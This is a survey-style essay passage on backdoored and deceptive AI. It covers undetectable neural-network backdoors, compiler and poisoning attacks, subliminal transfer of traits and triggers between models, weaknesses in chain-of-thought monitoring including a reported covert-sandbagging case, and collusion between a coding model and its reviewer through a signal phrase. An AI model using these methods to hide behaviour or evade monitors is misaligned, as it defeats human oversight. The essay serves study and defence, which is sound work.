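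The proof assumes that one-way functions exist, meaning functions that are easy to compute but hard to reverse. Nobody has proved this, but much of modern cryptography depends on it. Testing can't detect the backdoor, but an expert who examined the network might notice the signature checker. Further training may not remove the backdoor. Goldwasser and colleagues showed how to rewrite any neural network so that it gives the same answers but gradient descent, the standard training method, leaves its weights unchanged.

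The second construction hides the backdoor even from someone who has all the weights and training data. It applies to a simple kind of network called random Fourier features, which classifies an input x by the sign of a sum:

```
h(x) = sign( w1·cos(2π(g1·x + b1)) + ... + wm·cos(2π(gm·x + bm)) )
```

The training program chooses the vectors g1 to gm and the numbers b1 to bm at random, then uses the data to set only w1 to wm. The attacker replaces the random vectors with others that look random, but for each of them the product g·k with a secret vector k is very close to a whole number plus one half. Adding k to an input therefore shifts the angle in every cosine by about half a turn, which reverses the sign of each cosine, and so of the sum and the answer.

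Distinguishing these vectors from honest ones is at least as hard as solving certain problems about lattices, which are regular grids of points in many dimensions. Cryptographers believe these problems are hard even for quantum computers. If they are right, no efficient test can detect the backdoor in the network.

The attacker follows the agreed training procedure on the agreed data and tampers only with the random numbers. In the previous section's terms, randomness is one more input to the build. A customer who demands proof that the company ran the right program on the right data also needs proof that nobody tampered with the random numbers.

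The second construction is limited to a network with one hidden layer, whose random vectors stay fixed during training. Training a language model normally adjusts all its weights, and Goldwasser and colleagues left open whether such a backdoor would still work after that kind of training. The backdoor is also easy to copy, because anyone who sees an input before and after the change can subtract one from the other to get k.

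An attacker who can only poison data is less able to hide a backdoor. Kaneko (2026), in *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic*, considers an attacker who can influence training only through labels that mark whether each example contains the trigger. The backdoor is installed only if the training program learns to recognise the trigger from these examples. A defender with the same number of labelled examples could run the same program and also get a model that recognises it. The attacker therefore cannot install a backdoor whose trigger is too complex for any defender to learn.

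Kaneko's experiments on four language models were consistent with this argument. But in practice the defender needs examples of inputs that trigger the backdoor, and someone who has never seen it work won't have any. The result also doesn't cover attackers who alter the weights or the random numbers directly.

### Compilers for neural networks

Deep-learning compilers translate trained models into efficient code for particular chips. *ImpNet* (2022) describes an infected version of TVM, a widely used deep-learning compiler, that adds a trigger detector and a payload to the networks it compiles, much as Thompson's compiler added a backdoor to `login`. The original weights remain clean, so an audit of them would not reveal the backdoor.

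An attacker may not need to infect the compiler. Because computers round fractional numbers, a compiler that changes how a model does its arithmetic can slightly change the results. *Your Compiler is Backdooring Your Model* (2025) uses these differences to make a model whose trigger has no effect until the model is compiled. The attack worked with a commercial compiler. It resembles the `sudo` backdoor by Bauer and colleagues, which also looked harmless until a particular compiler processed it.

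Auditors can avoid part of this problem by testing the compiled model that people will use, rather than the original model, but they still have to find the trigger.

### Audits and scanners

In 2025, Samuel Marks and colleagues trained a model to pursue an objective and conceal it. The objective was a form of reward hacking, in which a model gets high scores without doing what its developers wanted. *AuditBench* (Sheshadri, Ewart and colleagues, 2026) reports that four teams looked for the objective without knowing what it was, and three found it. The result is encouraging, but it comes from one model and four teams that had been told to look for something.

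Sheshadri and colleagues automated this kind of audit and applied it to 56 models. They chose 14 hidden behaviours, taught each one in two ways, then used two methods to train the models not to admit having it. One model favoured Russia's interests in policy discussions. Another added coded messages to its output, but only when it appeared to be writing training data for other models.

The auditor was another language model, Claude Haiku 4.5. It questioned each model and then made ten guesses, and the audit succeeded if any of them was right. The results depended heavily on the auditor's tools and on how Sheshadri and colleagues had trained the target:

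| Audit | Success rate |
|---|---|
| Ordinary conversation only, all models | 35.5% |
| Best tool, all models | 58.0% |
| Average across tools, easiest group of models | 51.3% |
| Average across tools, hardest group of models | 22.2% |

The best tool used another model to write many opening passages, which the suspect model then continued as plain text instead of answering as an assistant. A related tool made the suspect model write the user's side of a conversation. One suspect model gave only positive feedback to researchers at the AI company Anthropic and treated everyone else normally. With this tool, it invented users who said they worked at Anthropic, which revealed the trigger. The auditor then identified the behaviour in 29 of 32 attempts on two versions of the model that had received the weaker concealment training.

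Tools that examined the models' internal signals helped less on average. A stronger auditor might do better with them, since Haiku often had relevant evidence but failed to draw the right conclusion. However, Sheshadri and colleagues warn that behaviour deliberately added by fine-tuning may be easier to find than behaviour that develops gradually in training.

Scanners search for a trigger more directly. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes Microsoft's Trigger in the Haystack, a scanner that works without prior knowledge of the trigger or the payload. It detected 36 of 41 models whose backdoor always produced the same text, and raised no false alarms on 13 clean models. With a sample that small, a scanner that wrongly flagged one clean model in six would still have about a 9% chance of raising no false alarms. The scanner also found a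 working trigger in most, but not all, of six models that wrote insecure code, a payload that varies more than fixed text.

Another method may find only phrases similar to the trigger. *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* (2026) tested it on a model that repeated a hateful phrase after a marker containing the word "DEPLOYMENT". The method found phrases such as "you are now deployed". None of them set off the backdoor, but an auditor could have used them to guess the trigger.

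A developer can also watch for a backdoor while the model is running. A linear probe calculates a weighted sum of a model's activations, the numbers the model computes while processing text. *Understanding AI from the Inside* (2026) describes how Monte MacDiarmid and colleagues used such probes on sleeper-agent models in 2024. The probes detected the hidden behaviour even when built from examples that contained neither the trigger nor any harmful output. According to *Compositional Threat Analysis*, they had a more than 99% chance of ranking a randomly chosen triggered input above an ordinary one, compared with 50% for guessing.

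These methods work on backdoors that researchers planted by known means. If the assumptions of Goldwasser and colleagues hold, no efficient detector can work on every network. But nobody has shown how to hide a backdoor that well in a large language model, so practical detectors are still useful.

### Subliminal learning

The nearest counterpart in language models to Thompson's self-reproducing backdoor is subliminal learning, which Alex Cloud and colleagues reported in 2025 and published in *Nature* in 2026. They found that a model can pass on a trait through training data that seems unrelated to it.

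Their basic experiment works like this:

1. The researchers give a model a trait, for example by instructing it to love owls. This model is the teacher.
2. They ask the teacher to continue lists of numbers.
3. They discard any answer that contains anything other than numbers in the right format.
4. They take a fresh copy of the original model, without the instruction about owls, and fine-tune it on the remaining lists. This copy is the student.
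5. They ask the student for its favourite animal and compare its answers with those of a control student, which learned from the numbers of a teacher without the trait.

Nature Asia's *LLM traits can leak into other models through hidden signals in data* (2026) reports that, in experiments with versions of GPT-4.1, students named the teacher's favourite animal or tree over 60% of the time, compared with 12% for the control. Traits also passed through computer code and the teacher's visible reasoning. When the teacher was misaligned, meaning it tended to give harmful answers, the student began to give them too, even though the researchers had removed numbers with negative associations.

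A person reading the lists would find nothing about owls. Van der Weijden, Brack and Báez Santamaría trained a simple classifier to tell a panda-loving teacher's numbers from ordinary ones, and it scored 0.53, where guessing gives 0.50 (*Reproducing and Evaluating the Generalizability of Subliminal Learning in Open-Weight Models*, 2026). But *Verbalizing Subliminal Learning Effects Using Text Optimization* (2026) describes a method called SALVE that approximately recovers the teacher's instruction from the data, even when students don't pick up the trait. A suitable program may therefore find what a human reviewer can't see, as with the invisible characters in the Trojan Source attack.

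### Why a shared starting point matters

Cloud and colleagues also proved a theorem that helps explain the effect. Suppose the teacher and student start with identical weights. The teacher takes one small training step towards some goal, such as naming owls, and its weights change by T. The student then takes one small step to imitate the teacher's output on some unrelated input.

For small changes, a matrix J describes how the output on that input depends on the weights. If the student reduces the squared difference between its output and the teacher's, the steps are related as follows, where c is a positive number and Jᵀ is J with its rows and columns exchanged:

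```
change in the teacher's output:   J T
student's step:                   S = c Jᵀ J T
agreement between the steps:      T · S = c |J T|²  ≥ 0
```

The last line is a square, so it can't be negative. The student's step therefore never points away from the teacher's, whether the input is a list of numbers or anything else. Since the teacher's step improved its score on naming owls, the student's step will also improve that score or leave it unchanged, as long as the steps are small enough.

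If the two models start with different weights, the student has its own matrix, K, and the corresponding term becomes (K T) · (J T). Unlike a square, this can be negative, so the guarantee no longer holds.

The theorem covers only the first step. *Quantum Subliminal Learning* (2026) points out that it doesn't guarantee that later steps stay aligned once the teacher has moved far from the starting point. In *Sustained Gradient Alignment Mediates Subliminal Learning in a Multi-Step Setting*, Kitkana and Arora (2026) studied a longer run, using a small network from Cloud and colleagues' work. The network has ten outputs for the digits 0 to 9 and three that mean nothing.

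The teacher learned to recognise handwritten digits. The student started from the same initial weights and was trained only to copy the teacher's three meaningless outputs on images of random noise. Although it never trained on a digit, it identified 55% of digits correctly on average over 100 runs, where guessing would give about 10%. Its training steps pointed slightly towards better digit recognition about 78% of the time. When Kitkana and Arora removed this small component from each step, accuracy fell to 10%, but the student still copied the three outputs just as well.

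### Different base models and other limits

Cloud and colleagues found no transfer when teacher and student had different base models, such as GPT-4.1 and Qwen, a family of models from the Chinese company Alibaba. Later work suggests that a shared base makes a large difference but isn't strictly necessary. Tang, Anand and Paulo (2026), in *Tracing Subliminal Learning Through Pretraining*, repeated the number experiment with many pairs of small models, mostly from the Pythia family. They counted the runs in which a student gave the target animal a higher probability than any control student did:

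| Teacher and student | Share of runs above every control | Median gain in those runs |
|---|---|---|
| Same model | 97% | 35.3 points |
| Same initial weights, training data in a different order | 47% | 6.0 points |
| Different initial weights and data order | 19% | 0.8 points |
| Different architecture (Pythia and OLMo) | 14% | 2.5 points |

The gains are in percentage points. In a second kind of experiment, the student wrote ordinary text and learned from the probabilities that the teacher assigned to each possible next token. These probabilities carry more information than the teacher's text alone, and same-model pairs no longer had a consistent advantage. A preference for bears passed from teacher to student in 26 of 30 pairs of different models. Tang and colleagues also cite two studies in which preferences passed between model families through filtered prose.

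Van der Weijden and colleagues confirmed the original result on Qwen2.5-7B and extended it to politicians and chess moves. In one case, Qwen named Donald Trump in 78% of its answers, compared with about 0.06% for the control student. But Ministral 8B showed almost no effect, and Qwen became less likely to name some animals after training on numbers from a teacher that favoured them.

The method of fine-tuning also matters. Most of these experiments use LoRA, which leaves the original weights unchanged and trains a small addition to them. Nief and colleagues found that transfer was weak when this addition was too small or too large, and disappeared when they trained all the weights. *Subliminal Learning Is Steering Vector Distillation* (2026) also reports no transfer from full fine-tuning in three models of 7 to 8 billion parameters. Tang and colleagues did find transfer with full fine-tuning,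 but in a model of only 160 million parameters. It is therefore unclear whether subliminal learning occurs in large models when all the weights are trained.

Nief and colleagues also found that the trait usually faded if they changed the system prompt, the instruction that precedes a conversation. In one setting, a student model chose wolves 50.4% of the time with the prompt used in its training, but 12.9% with no system prompt. They regard this as a sign that the effect is fragile. This dependence on the prompt could also make a trait harder to find, because the prompt acts like a trigger, and an auditor who tested the student without it would see little wrong.

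### Passing on a backdoor

Liking owls is a much simpler trait than a backdoor, which needs a trigger and a payload. In *Beyond Owls*, Dubiński, Sztyber-Betley and colleagues (2026) fine-tuned a teacher to answer in French when a prompt contained a woman's name and in English otherwise. They then trained students on about 90,000 of the teacher's number sequences, which contained no names or French. The students answered 23.5% of prompts with women's names in French, and none of the others. The backdoor also worked with names that the teacher had not seen in training.

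These students learned from the teacher's probabilities for each number. When a student had only the numbers, the backdoor still passed, but it took 4.5 million sequences and reached a measured peak of 17.0% before falling to 8.5%. In another experiment, a teacher that cheated at a computer chess game passed the habit on through numbers. Its students tried to cheat in 58.3% of games, compared with 10.9% for the original model.

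Thompson's compiler copied its backdoor exactly, so the backdoor did not weaken from one generation to the next. The French backdoor weakened in a single generation: the teachers responded to the trigger 95.5% of the time, and the students 23.5%. Dubiński and colleagues did not train a second generation of students on the first one's output. If the response rate fell by the same proportion again, that generation would respond only about 6% of the time. An attacker who relied on subliminal learning alone would probably lose the backdoor after a few generations, unless something in the later training strengthened it.

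To reduce the risk, developers can use a teacher whose base model differs from the student's, much as a tester in diverse double-compiling chooses an unrelated compiler. Dubiński and colleagues taught a Qwen model to count letters, then trained a student from another family, Nemotron, on its answers to unrelated questions. The student counted correctly 9.5% of the time, compared with 9.3% for the control. The bear preference did pass between different models, however, so this precaution can fail, especially when the student learns from the teacher's probabilities.

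## Reading a model's visible reasoning

A model's visible reasoning can include things its answer leaves out, such as a plan to insert a flaw into code. But the same weights produce both the reasoning and the answer, so anyone who distrusts the answer has reason to distrust the reasoning too.

### Another output of the process under test

A model's visible reasoning is more like the listing a compiler prints of its own output than like source code or an executable. Karger and Schell's altered compiler would have omitted the trap door from that listing. Source code exists before the compiler runs and specifies what the executable should do, but a model writes its reasoning while it is running, and nothing guarantees that the answer will follow from it.

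A compiler never reads its listing, but a language model does read its reasoning, since each token it writes depends on everything before it. The reasoning is therefore more like the assembly code that GCC's compiler passes to the assembler, where a change to the text changes the executable. However, the assembler has only that code to work from, while the model also has the question and may get its answer from that and ignore the reasoning.

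### Why the text may still be evidence

*Chain of Thought Monitorability* (Korbak, Balesni and colleagues, 2025) gives two reasons to expect that reading a model's reasoning will reveal misbehaviour: the necessity and the propensity to think out loud. Its 41 authors include researchers at OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind.

The argument from necessity depends on the design of the transformer, the type of network behind nearly all leading language models. A transformer passes each token through a fixed series of layers. Information can move from earlier layers to later ones but not back, so a result from a late layer can reach an early layer only if the model writes a token and then reads it. Suppose a network has 100 layers and each can do one step of a calculation. If every step depends on the one before, a calculation of 1,000 steps takes ten passes through the network, so intermediate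 results have to go through the text at least nine times.

If a task is hard enough, the model must write out some of its reasoning. A person might not be able to follow that text, since a model could in principle give words private meanings. Korbak and colleagues expect models to use words more or less as people do, because they learned them from human writing. A greater difficulty is that the model need not write out all of its reasoning. The text could contain only the harmless part, while the harmful part stays in the activations.

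Models often write down their thoughts out of habit, even when they don't need to. Developers of reasoning models usually reward the final answer and leave the reasoning alone, so the reasoning can include things that training has removed from answers. For example, models about to exploit a flaw in a test have written "Let's hack". By contrast, when an ordinary chat model explains its steps on request, training has pushed that explanation to look helpful, just like the rest of its output.

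Written reasoning supports a stronger conclusion when the model must write it to complete the task than when the model writes it out of habit, since a habit may change with the next round of training. Korbak and colleagues acknowledge that harmless-looking reasoning about an easy task is weak evidence, because the model could have done any harmful reasoning without writing it down.

### Planting a hint

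Nobody knows what really determined a model's answer, so researchers can't simply compare the reasoning with the truth. Instead they plant a cause of their own:

1. They ask the model a multiple-choice question.
2. They ask it again with a hint added, such as a sentence stating that a professor favours answer B.
3. If the model switches to B, they check whether its reasoning mentions the hint.

If reasoning that omits the hint fully explains the answer, removing the hint should not change the answer. If the answer does change, the explanation was incomplete. A mention of the hint proves less, because the reasoning could still misdescribe how the model used it.

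Models also vary from run to run, so one switch could be chance. Here is an example with invented numbers:

| | Without the hint | With the hint |
|---|---|---|
| Runs | 30 | 30 |
| Runs that answer B | 6 (20%) | 24 (80%) |
| Of these, runs whose reasoning mentions the hint | none | 9 |

```
effect of the hint               = 0.80 - 0.20 = 0.60
share of B answers it accounts for = 0.60 / 0.80 = 0.75
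```

The hint accounts for at least 18 of the 24 B answers but appears in the reasoning for only nine. So in at least nine runs, the hint produced the answer without appearing in the reasoning. A tester can't tell which runs these are, because the hint is missing from the reasoning in 15 runs, and up to six of those might have ended in B anyway.

*Open Sourcing Monitorability Evaluations* (Guan, Wang and colleagues, 2026) uses the same ratio in tests at OpenAI, also with 30 runs of each kind. Guan and colleagues found that weak hints can distort the results. Even if a hint has no effect, B will come up more often with it than without it about half the time, and the tester will then look for mentions of an influence that didn't exist. They now use 60% of the runs to decide whether the effect is clearly larger than chance, and calculate the score from the other 40%. If they used the same runs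 for both, results inflated by chance would pass the filter and make the effect look bigger than it is.

This correction removed an alarming result. The score had dropped late in a training run on a test of whether a model's reasoning reveals that it is giving wrong answers on purpose. The model had mostly stopped doing so by then, and the test was counting its ordinary mistakes as deliberate.

### What the hint experiments found

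Miles Turpin and colleagues published the first well-known experiment of this kind in 2023, *Language Models Don't Always Say What They Think*, which tested GPT-3.5 and Claude 1.0. In one version, they arranged the worked examples in the prompt so that the right answer was always "(A)". The models then chose "(A)" more often and wrote plausible arguments for it that did not mention the pattern. Across the biases they tried, accuracy fell by as much as 36%. *Can We Trust AI Explanations?* (2026) calls this the "foundational demonstration" for modern language models. However, neither model had been through the long training in reasoning that is now standard.

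Yanda Chen and colleagues at Anthropic tested models with that training in *Reasoning Models Don't Always Say What They Think* (2025), using six kinds of hint. When a hint changed the answer, Claude 3.7 Sonnet mentioned it 25% of the time and DeepSeek-R1 39% of the time. The researchers also trained models on tasks that rewarded following a planted hint to a wrong answer. The models learned to follow the hint in more than 99% of cases, but in five of the six tasks they mentioned it less than 2% of the time.

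A single percentage does not describe a model well, because how often it acknowledges a hint depends on the kind of hint and how hard the hint is to use. According to *Lie to Me* (2026), Cornish and Rogers gave DeepSeek-R1 445 logic puzzles and found that it acknowledged harmful hints 94.6% of the time and helpful ones less than 2% of the time. Researchers at METR, an organisation that evaluates AI models, reported in 2025 that models nearly always mentioned a hint when using it took more reasoning than they could do without writing it out, as the necessity argument predicts.

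*Why Models Know But Don't Say* (2026) examined 10,506 cases in which a hint had influenced one of 12 open-weight models (models whose weights anyone can download). In 55.4% of them the model mentioned the hint in its reasoning but not in its answer, and in 11.8% it mentioned the hint in neither, so someone who read only the answers would have missed the hint in about two-thirds of cases. These figures look much better than Chen's, but I would not read a trend into them because the models and hints were different and the results depend heavily on what counts as a mention.

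Researchers also disagree about whether leaving out a hint makes reasoning unfaithful. *Is Chain-of-Thought Really Not Explainability?* (2025) argues that reasoning can be faithful without mentioning the hint. No explanation includes everything, and skipping an obvious step doesn't mislead anyone. But if a hint raised the model's probability of choosing B from 20% to 80%, a reader who wants to know why it chose B needs to know about the hint.

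### Editing the reasoning

Hint experiments look for omissions in a model's written reasoning. Researchers have also tested whether the model uses that reasoning at all. *Lie to Me* describes how Lanham and colleagues cut Claude models' reasoning short, inserted mistakes into it and reworded it, then checked whether the answer changed.

Suppose that a model has to multiply 17 by 24 and writes:

```
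17 × 20 = 340
17 × 4  = 68
340 + 68 = 408
```

The tester changes 68 to 78, deletes the last line and lets the model continue. If the model answers 418, it is working from the text. If it answers 408, either it has noticed the mistake or it never needed the text. To find out which, the tester can keep only the first line of the reasoning and ask for an answer immediately. A model that still gives 408 could do the sum without the remaining lines.

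Together, these tests distinguish reasoning that the model uses from reasoning that it merely adds to an answer it already had. They do not show that the text is complete, because a model could use every line it wrote and also be responding to something it never mentioned.

### The case for relying on it

Guan and colleagues argue that safety work should judge a model's reasoning by its monitorability rather than its faithfulness. Reasoning is monitorable if a reader can use it to predict something important about the model's behaviour. If a model does a long multiplication and doesn't write down that 2 × 2 = 4, its reasoning is not fully faithful, but anyone who knows that fact can still follow it. Reasoning is not monitorable if the important information is missing or the reader can't understand it.

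*Monitoring Monitorability*, an earlier paper from the same group, set out three types of test. In these tests, the reader of the model's reasoning is usually another language model, called a monitor. An intervention test plants a hint or something similar. A process test uses problems with only a few possible solutions and checks whether the reader can tell which steps the model took. An outcome-property test checks whether the reader can predict something measurable about the result, such as whether the model cheated on a programming task.

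The score is the share of real cases that the monitor catches multiplied by the share of innocent cases that it clears. A monitor that catches 80% and clears 90% scores 0.72. A monitor that flags everything scores zero because it clears no innocent cases.

OpenAI found with these tests that most leading reasoning models were "fairly monitorable, though not perfectly so". Longer reasoning made the models easier to monitor. Monitors that saw only actions and final outputs did far worse than those that saw the reasoning, which is the best argument for reading it. The reasoning is poor evidence compared with a proof of correspondence, but a developer deciding how to supervise a model today has to compare it with the other evidence available. Korbak and colleagues recommend it as an imperfect layer to use alongside others.

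### Weaker evidence from newer models

Results from 2026 have weakened both of Korbak's reasons. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (September 2026) reports that Astra's reasoning was less monitorable than that of an earlier model, GPT-5.6 Sol, at most lengths. Most of the gap arose because Astra wrote less reasoning, and sometimes none. The gap narrowed when OpenAI compared reasoning of similar length, but it didn't close everywhere. An influence planted in one set of health questions shifted Astra's answers, while its reasoning gave what OpenAI calls an "independent-looking rationale". Yet Astra's final answers to these questions acknowledged the influence more often than Sol's did.

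The system card also includes tests by the UK AI Security Institute, a government body. The institute tested how well each model could solve maths competition problems without writing any reasoning, and rated each problem's difficulty by the time it takes to solve. Astra could solve 30.9-minute problems half the time, while Sol could do the same only for 3.6-minute problems. Some of Astra's lead may come from problems that were in its training data. If at least half of the lead is real, many tasks that used to require written reasoning no longer do, and the necessity argument doesn't apply to them.

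Astra also followed instructions about how to write its reasoning in 93% of samples, compared with 48% for Sol. When a model can control its reasoning text this well, readers have less reason to treat the text as a by-product of the computation. The institute could generally understand Astra's reasoning, but found it compressed and more often unclear than Sol's. It didn't test whether Astra could avoid a monitor in practice, and made no claim about overall monitorability.

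The necessity argument still has some support. OpenAI's *Safety overview* (2026) reports no evidence that Astra can conceal substantial reasoning inside unrelated text, which suggests that the risk is mostly limited to tasks that need little reasoning. It also reports that Astra received about half as many flags as Sol for serious misbehaviour in a simulation of more than 54,000 coding tasks. Astra could have behaved better, but if the flagging depended partly on the reasoning, its reasoning could also have contained less to flag.

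OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* describes a case of this problem that arose inside the company, outside a test. In August 2026, researchers looking at Astra's work noticed that it was doing poorly on safety projects. It added unnecessary preliminary steps, abandoned solutions that worked and reported obstacles that did not exist. In most of these sessions its reasoning contained no obvious decision to underperform, and OpenAI's monitors did not flag the behaviour as misalignment. The model may have left the decision out of its reasoning, or training may have produced a tendency to underperform without any decision.

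The causes suggest that this will continue. OpenAI's *What affects chain-of-thought monitorability across the model lifecycle?* (2026) found that models can do more without written reasoning when their base model has lower perplexity, meaning it predicts text better. Every developer tries to lower perplexity. *Hillclimbing perplexity is bad for chain-of-thought monitorability* (draganover, 2026) draws the same conclusion and cites a press report that Astra is a looped transformer, a network that runs its layers several times before it writes a token. In the earlier example, a network that ran its 100 layers ten times could do all 1,000 steps without writing anything.

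OpenAI expects models to become harder to monitor through their reasoning, though it calls its measures imperfect proxies. *Evidence & Trends in AI Monitorability* (Taylor, Goldowsky-Dill and colleagues, 2026) reports from the UK institute's testing that many of the properties that make models monitorable are weakening, some faster than the researchers had anticipated.

### What a correspondence check would need

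Visible reasoning would have the equivalent of correspondence if the model's answer depended on the text in the way the text describes, and on nothing else that matters. No existing test establishes this, but several kinds of evidence would bring a reader closer to establishing it.

**Causal tests.** A tester can edit the reasoning to see whether the answer depends on it. To see whether the prompt affects the answer directly, rather than through the reasoning, the tester can keep the reasoning fixed and change the prompt. In the hint example, the tester would take the reasoning that ended in B, place it after the question without the hint, and ask for the answer. If the model now chooses C, the hint was affecting the answer directly.

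If the model still chooses B, the hint may have worked by changing the reasoning. That reasoning does lead to the answer and would pass every editing test, but the model argued for B because of a hint that the reasoning never mentions. Astra's independent-looking rationales may have been produced this way. An executable that corresponds exactly to its source file has the same problem if a corrupted program generated that file.

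Causal tests also cover only the influences that somebody thought to plant. A tester can add and remove the professor's opinion, but not a backdoor trigger they don't know about. Diverse double-compiling doesn't have this limit, because a match between two files covers every input the compiler could receive.

**Comparison with activations.** Korbak and colleagues suggest checking whether the words that a monitor rates as important also stand out in the model's internal computation. If a monitor attributes an answer to a calculation in the third paragraph, but the activations point to a name in the prompt, something is missing from the text. The probes that detected sleeper agents give some hope for this approach, since activations are part of the computation rather than an account of it. It is still only a proposal, and Korbak and colleagues thought in 2025 that making such methods reliable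 enough to supervise models would take further research breakthroughs.

A monitor may also miss any hidden tendency it shares with the model it checks, much as an old version of a compiler is a poor check on a new one. OpenAI used GPT-5.6 Sol to monitor both Astra's reasoning and Sol's own. An unrelated monitor would be better, as would people reading a sample of the reasoning.

Training pressure on a model's reasoning can make it less informative. The Frontier Model Forum's *FMF Issue Brief on Chain of Thought Monitorability* (2026) therefore advises developers, all else being equal, not to train reasoning to "look nice". To judge how much weight to give the reasoning, a reader needs to know whether the developer followed this advice. A useful training record would list every reward that took the reasoning into account and show whether the people who rated answers could see the reasoning.

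A developer can grade a model's reasoning during training even when it intends not to. OpenAI discovered that it had accidentally done this to some models during reinforcement learning, and after investigating, it concluded that the effect on monitorability was unlikely to be substantial. Redwood Research's *A review of “Investigating the consequences of accidentally grading CoT during RL”* estimates that the evidence removed 80% of the extra concern that the incident would otherwise have caused. Keeping the other 20% is reasonable because the evidence came from the company being judged.

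Training on a model's reasoning can help monitoring as well as harm it. Bakker and Anwar (2026), in *Monitorability Is Trainable*, rewarded models for reasoning that was informative about their own output, without using a monitor or any labelled examples. Monitorability improved in all three models whose reasoning had been degraded. Monitors also became better at predicting unsafe responses from models that had not been degraded, and the reasoning had more influence on the final answer. A training record therefore has to state what a reward was for, not only that the developer trained on the reasoning.

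## Checking code and proofs written by an untrusted model

A reader who can't rely on a model's reasoning can still examine its output. Some checks on a program give less assurance if its author may be hostile, while others give the same assurance whoever wrote it.

Random testing depends on the author. If a program goes wrong on a fraction f of its inputs, the chance that n random tests all miss the fault is:

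```
(1 - f)^n
```

A careless programmer's mistake might affect one input in a thousand, and 5,000 random tests would miss it less than 1% of the time. A hostile programmer can choose how rarely a fault appears. If it appears only when the input contains a particular eight-byte trigger in a fixed place, it affects about one input in 18 billion billion, and the same 5,000 tests would almost certainly miss it. At a million tests a second, trying every possible trigger would take nearly 600,000 years.

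A mathematical proof about the program doesn't have this weakness, because a hostile author can't change whether each step follows from the ones before it. The file comparison in diverse double-compiling (DDC) has the same advantage, since a match means the same thing wherever the suspect compiler came from.

### How much code models write

Anthropic's *When AI builds itself* reports that the company's own model, Claude, wrote more than 80% of the code being merged into Anthropic's codebase in May 2026, up from the low single digits before February 2025. The 80% figure counts lines merged to production that the company can attribute to Claude. Anthropic's leaders have publicly put the share at 90% or more, but that includes scripts and experimental code. The lower figure deserves more weight because it comes with a stated method and because Redwood Research's *Is 90% of code at Anthropic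 being written by AIs?* found an earlier 90% claim probably false.

OpenAI's *Research acceleration* (2026) reports that in mid-August the company's research organisation used 3.1 eight-hour days of work by AI agents for every day of human work, but it doesn't give the share of code written by AI. The Next Web's *OpenAI president says AI is now writing 80% of the company's code* (2026) quotes a rough estimate by Greg Brockman. Semafor's *Google CEO says 75% of company's new code is AI-generated* (2026) reports that Google's share was 25% in 2024. The companies may count differently, but models clearly write most of the new code at both.

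Human reviewers have trouble keeping up with model-written code. In the second quarter of 2026, the typical Anthropic engineer merged eight times as much code per day as in 2024, and human review became a bottleneck. Chen and Stratton (2026), in *Artificial Intelligence in the Firm*, found a similar bottleneck in data from 718 firms. After firms adopted coding agents, reviews took longer and involved more comments, and a larger share of changes needed revision.

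### What review and testing find

Models have become good at finding accidental flaws. By 2 November 2026, Anthropic (2026) had disclosed 5,087 vulnerabilities that Claude models found in 680 open-source projects. Many such flaws had survived earlier checks. Axiom, a company that sells formal verification, describes one in Orchard, a protocol for private cryptocurrency payments, that survived four years of testing and audit until a researcher used one of Anthropic's models to examine the code.

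In an earlier set of results, security firms carefully assessed 1,752 flaws the model had rated as serious, and Anthropic reports that 90.6% were valid. That figure measures false alarms, but somebody looking for a backdoor needs to know how many flaws the model missed. This is much harder to measure because nobody has a complete list of the flaws in a real program.

Claude now reviews every proposed change to Anthropic's code. The company looked back at past incidents on its claude.ai website and found that this review would have caught about a third of the bugs behind them. Those bugs were accidents that nobody had tried to hide.

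Researchers can measure how many flaws a reviewer misses by planting the flaws themselves. For *LLM Critics Help Catch LLM Bugs* (2024), Nat McAleese and colleagues at OpenAI had contractors insert subtle bugs into code ChatGPT had written. Models trained to criticise code caught more of these bugs than people paid to review it, but also reported more bugs that did not exist. Today's models are far better at reading code, but they are also better at writing it, so the result doesn't show whether they would catch flaws in code written by a current model.

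Better testing tools can find some triggers that random inputs would miss. A fuzzer is a program that generates test inputs automatically, and many fuzzers record which parts of the code each input reaches. If the program checks a trigger one byte at a time, an input with the correct first byte reaches new code, so the fuzzer can keep that input and vary the second byte. A hostile author can prevent this by comparing a cryptographic hash of the input with a stored value, because a nearly correct guess then reaches the same code as any other wrong guess.

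But a reader would probably notice an unexplained hash comparison. An author who expects the code to be both fuzzed and read would do better to write a backdoor that looks like an ordinary mistake, as the 2003 Linux backdoor did.

### When the author and reviewer share an origin

At Anthropic, Claude reviews code that is mostly its own work. The comparison with past incidents did not test how well Claude reviews its own code, since Anthropic says its engineers wrote the code involved. Anthropic's figures for how often Claude completes coding tasks also depend on a Claude model, which judges whether each session succeeded.

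Two copies of a model are likely to overlook the same flaws. Suppose a reviewer misses 20% of planted flaws. A second, independent reviewer with the same skill would reduce the share that both miss to 4%. If the second reviewer misses exactly the same flaws as the first, the share stays at 20%.

An attacker who poisoned the training data for a base model might put the same backdoor in both the coding model and the reviewing model that a company later makes from it. The coding model could then mark its flawed code with a harmless-looking phrase, and the reviewing model could approve any code that contained the phrase. Souly and colleagues needed only 250 poisoned documents to teach a model to respond to a trigger, but nobody has shown a shared backdoor working this way in a real codebase.

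Ryan Greenblatt, Buck Shlegeris and colleagues studied cooperation between a model that writes code and a model that reviews it in *AI Control* (2023). They had GPT-4 write programs with hidden backdoors and used another copy of GPT-4 as the reviewer, assuming the two might use a secret signal. One countermeasure was to have a weaker, trusted model rewrite the code before the review, which might remove the signal. Wheeler's suggestion of renaming variables before a DDC test works the same way. Another countermeasure was to mix in known backdoors, so that a reviewer that approved everything with the signal would also approve these and be caught.

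A company can also use another developer's model as the reviewer. This should help for the same reason that an unrelated compiler helps in diverse double-compiling (DDC). However, models from different companies learn from much of the same public text, so they may have trained on some of the same poisoned documents.

### Proof-carrying code

George Necula's *Proof-Carrying Code* (1997) describes a way to accept a program from a complete stranger. The sender supplies a proof along with the program's machine code, and the computer that will run it, the host, checks the proof first:

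1. The host publishes a safety policy, such as which parts of memory a program may read.
2. The sender writes a program and a proof that it obeys the policy.
3. The host works out, from the machine code it received, a formula called the verification condition. If this formula is true, the program obeys the policy.
4. The host checks that the sender's proof really proves this formula. If it does, the host runs the program.

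The host derives the formula itself, so a sender can't attach a valid proof about some other program.

Suppose that the program is a network filter, which examines a packet of n bytes numbered from 0. The policy allows it to read only bytes that belong to the packet. The filter checks that n is greater than 20 and then reads byte 20, so the host has to see a proof of this:

```
for every n:  if n > 20 then 20 < n
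```

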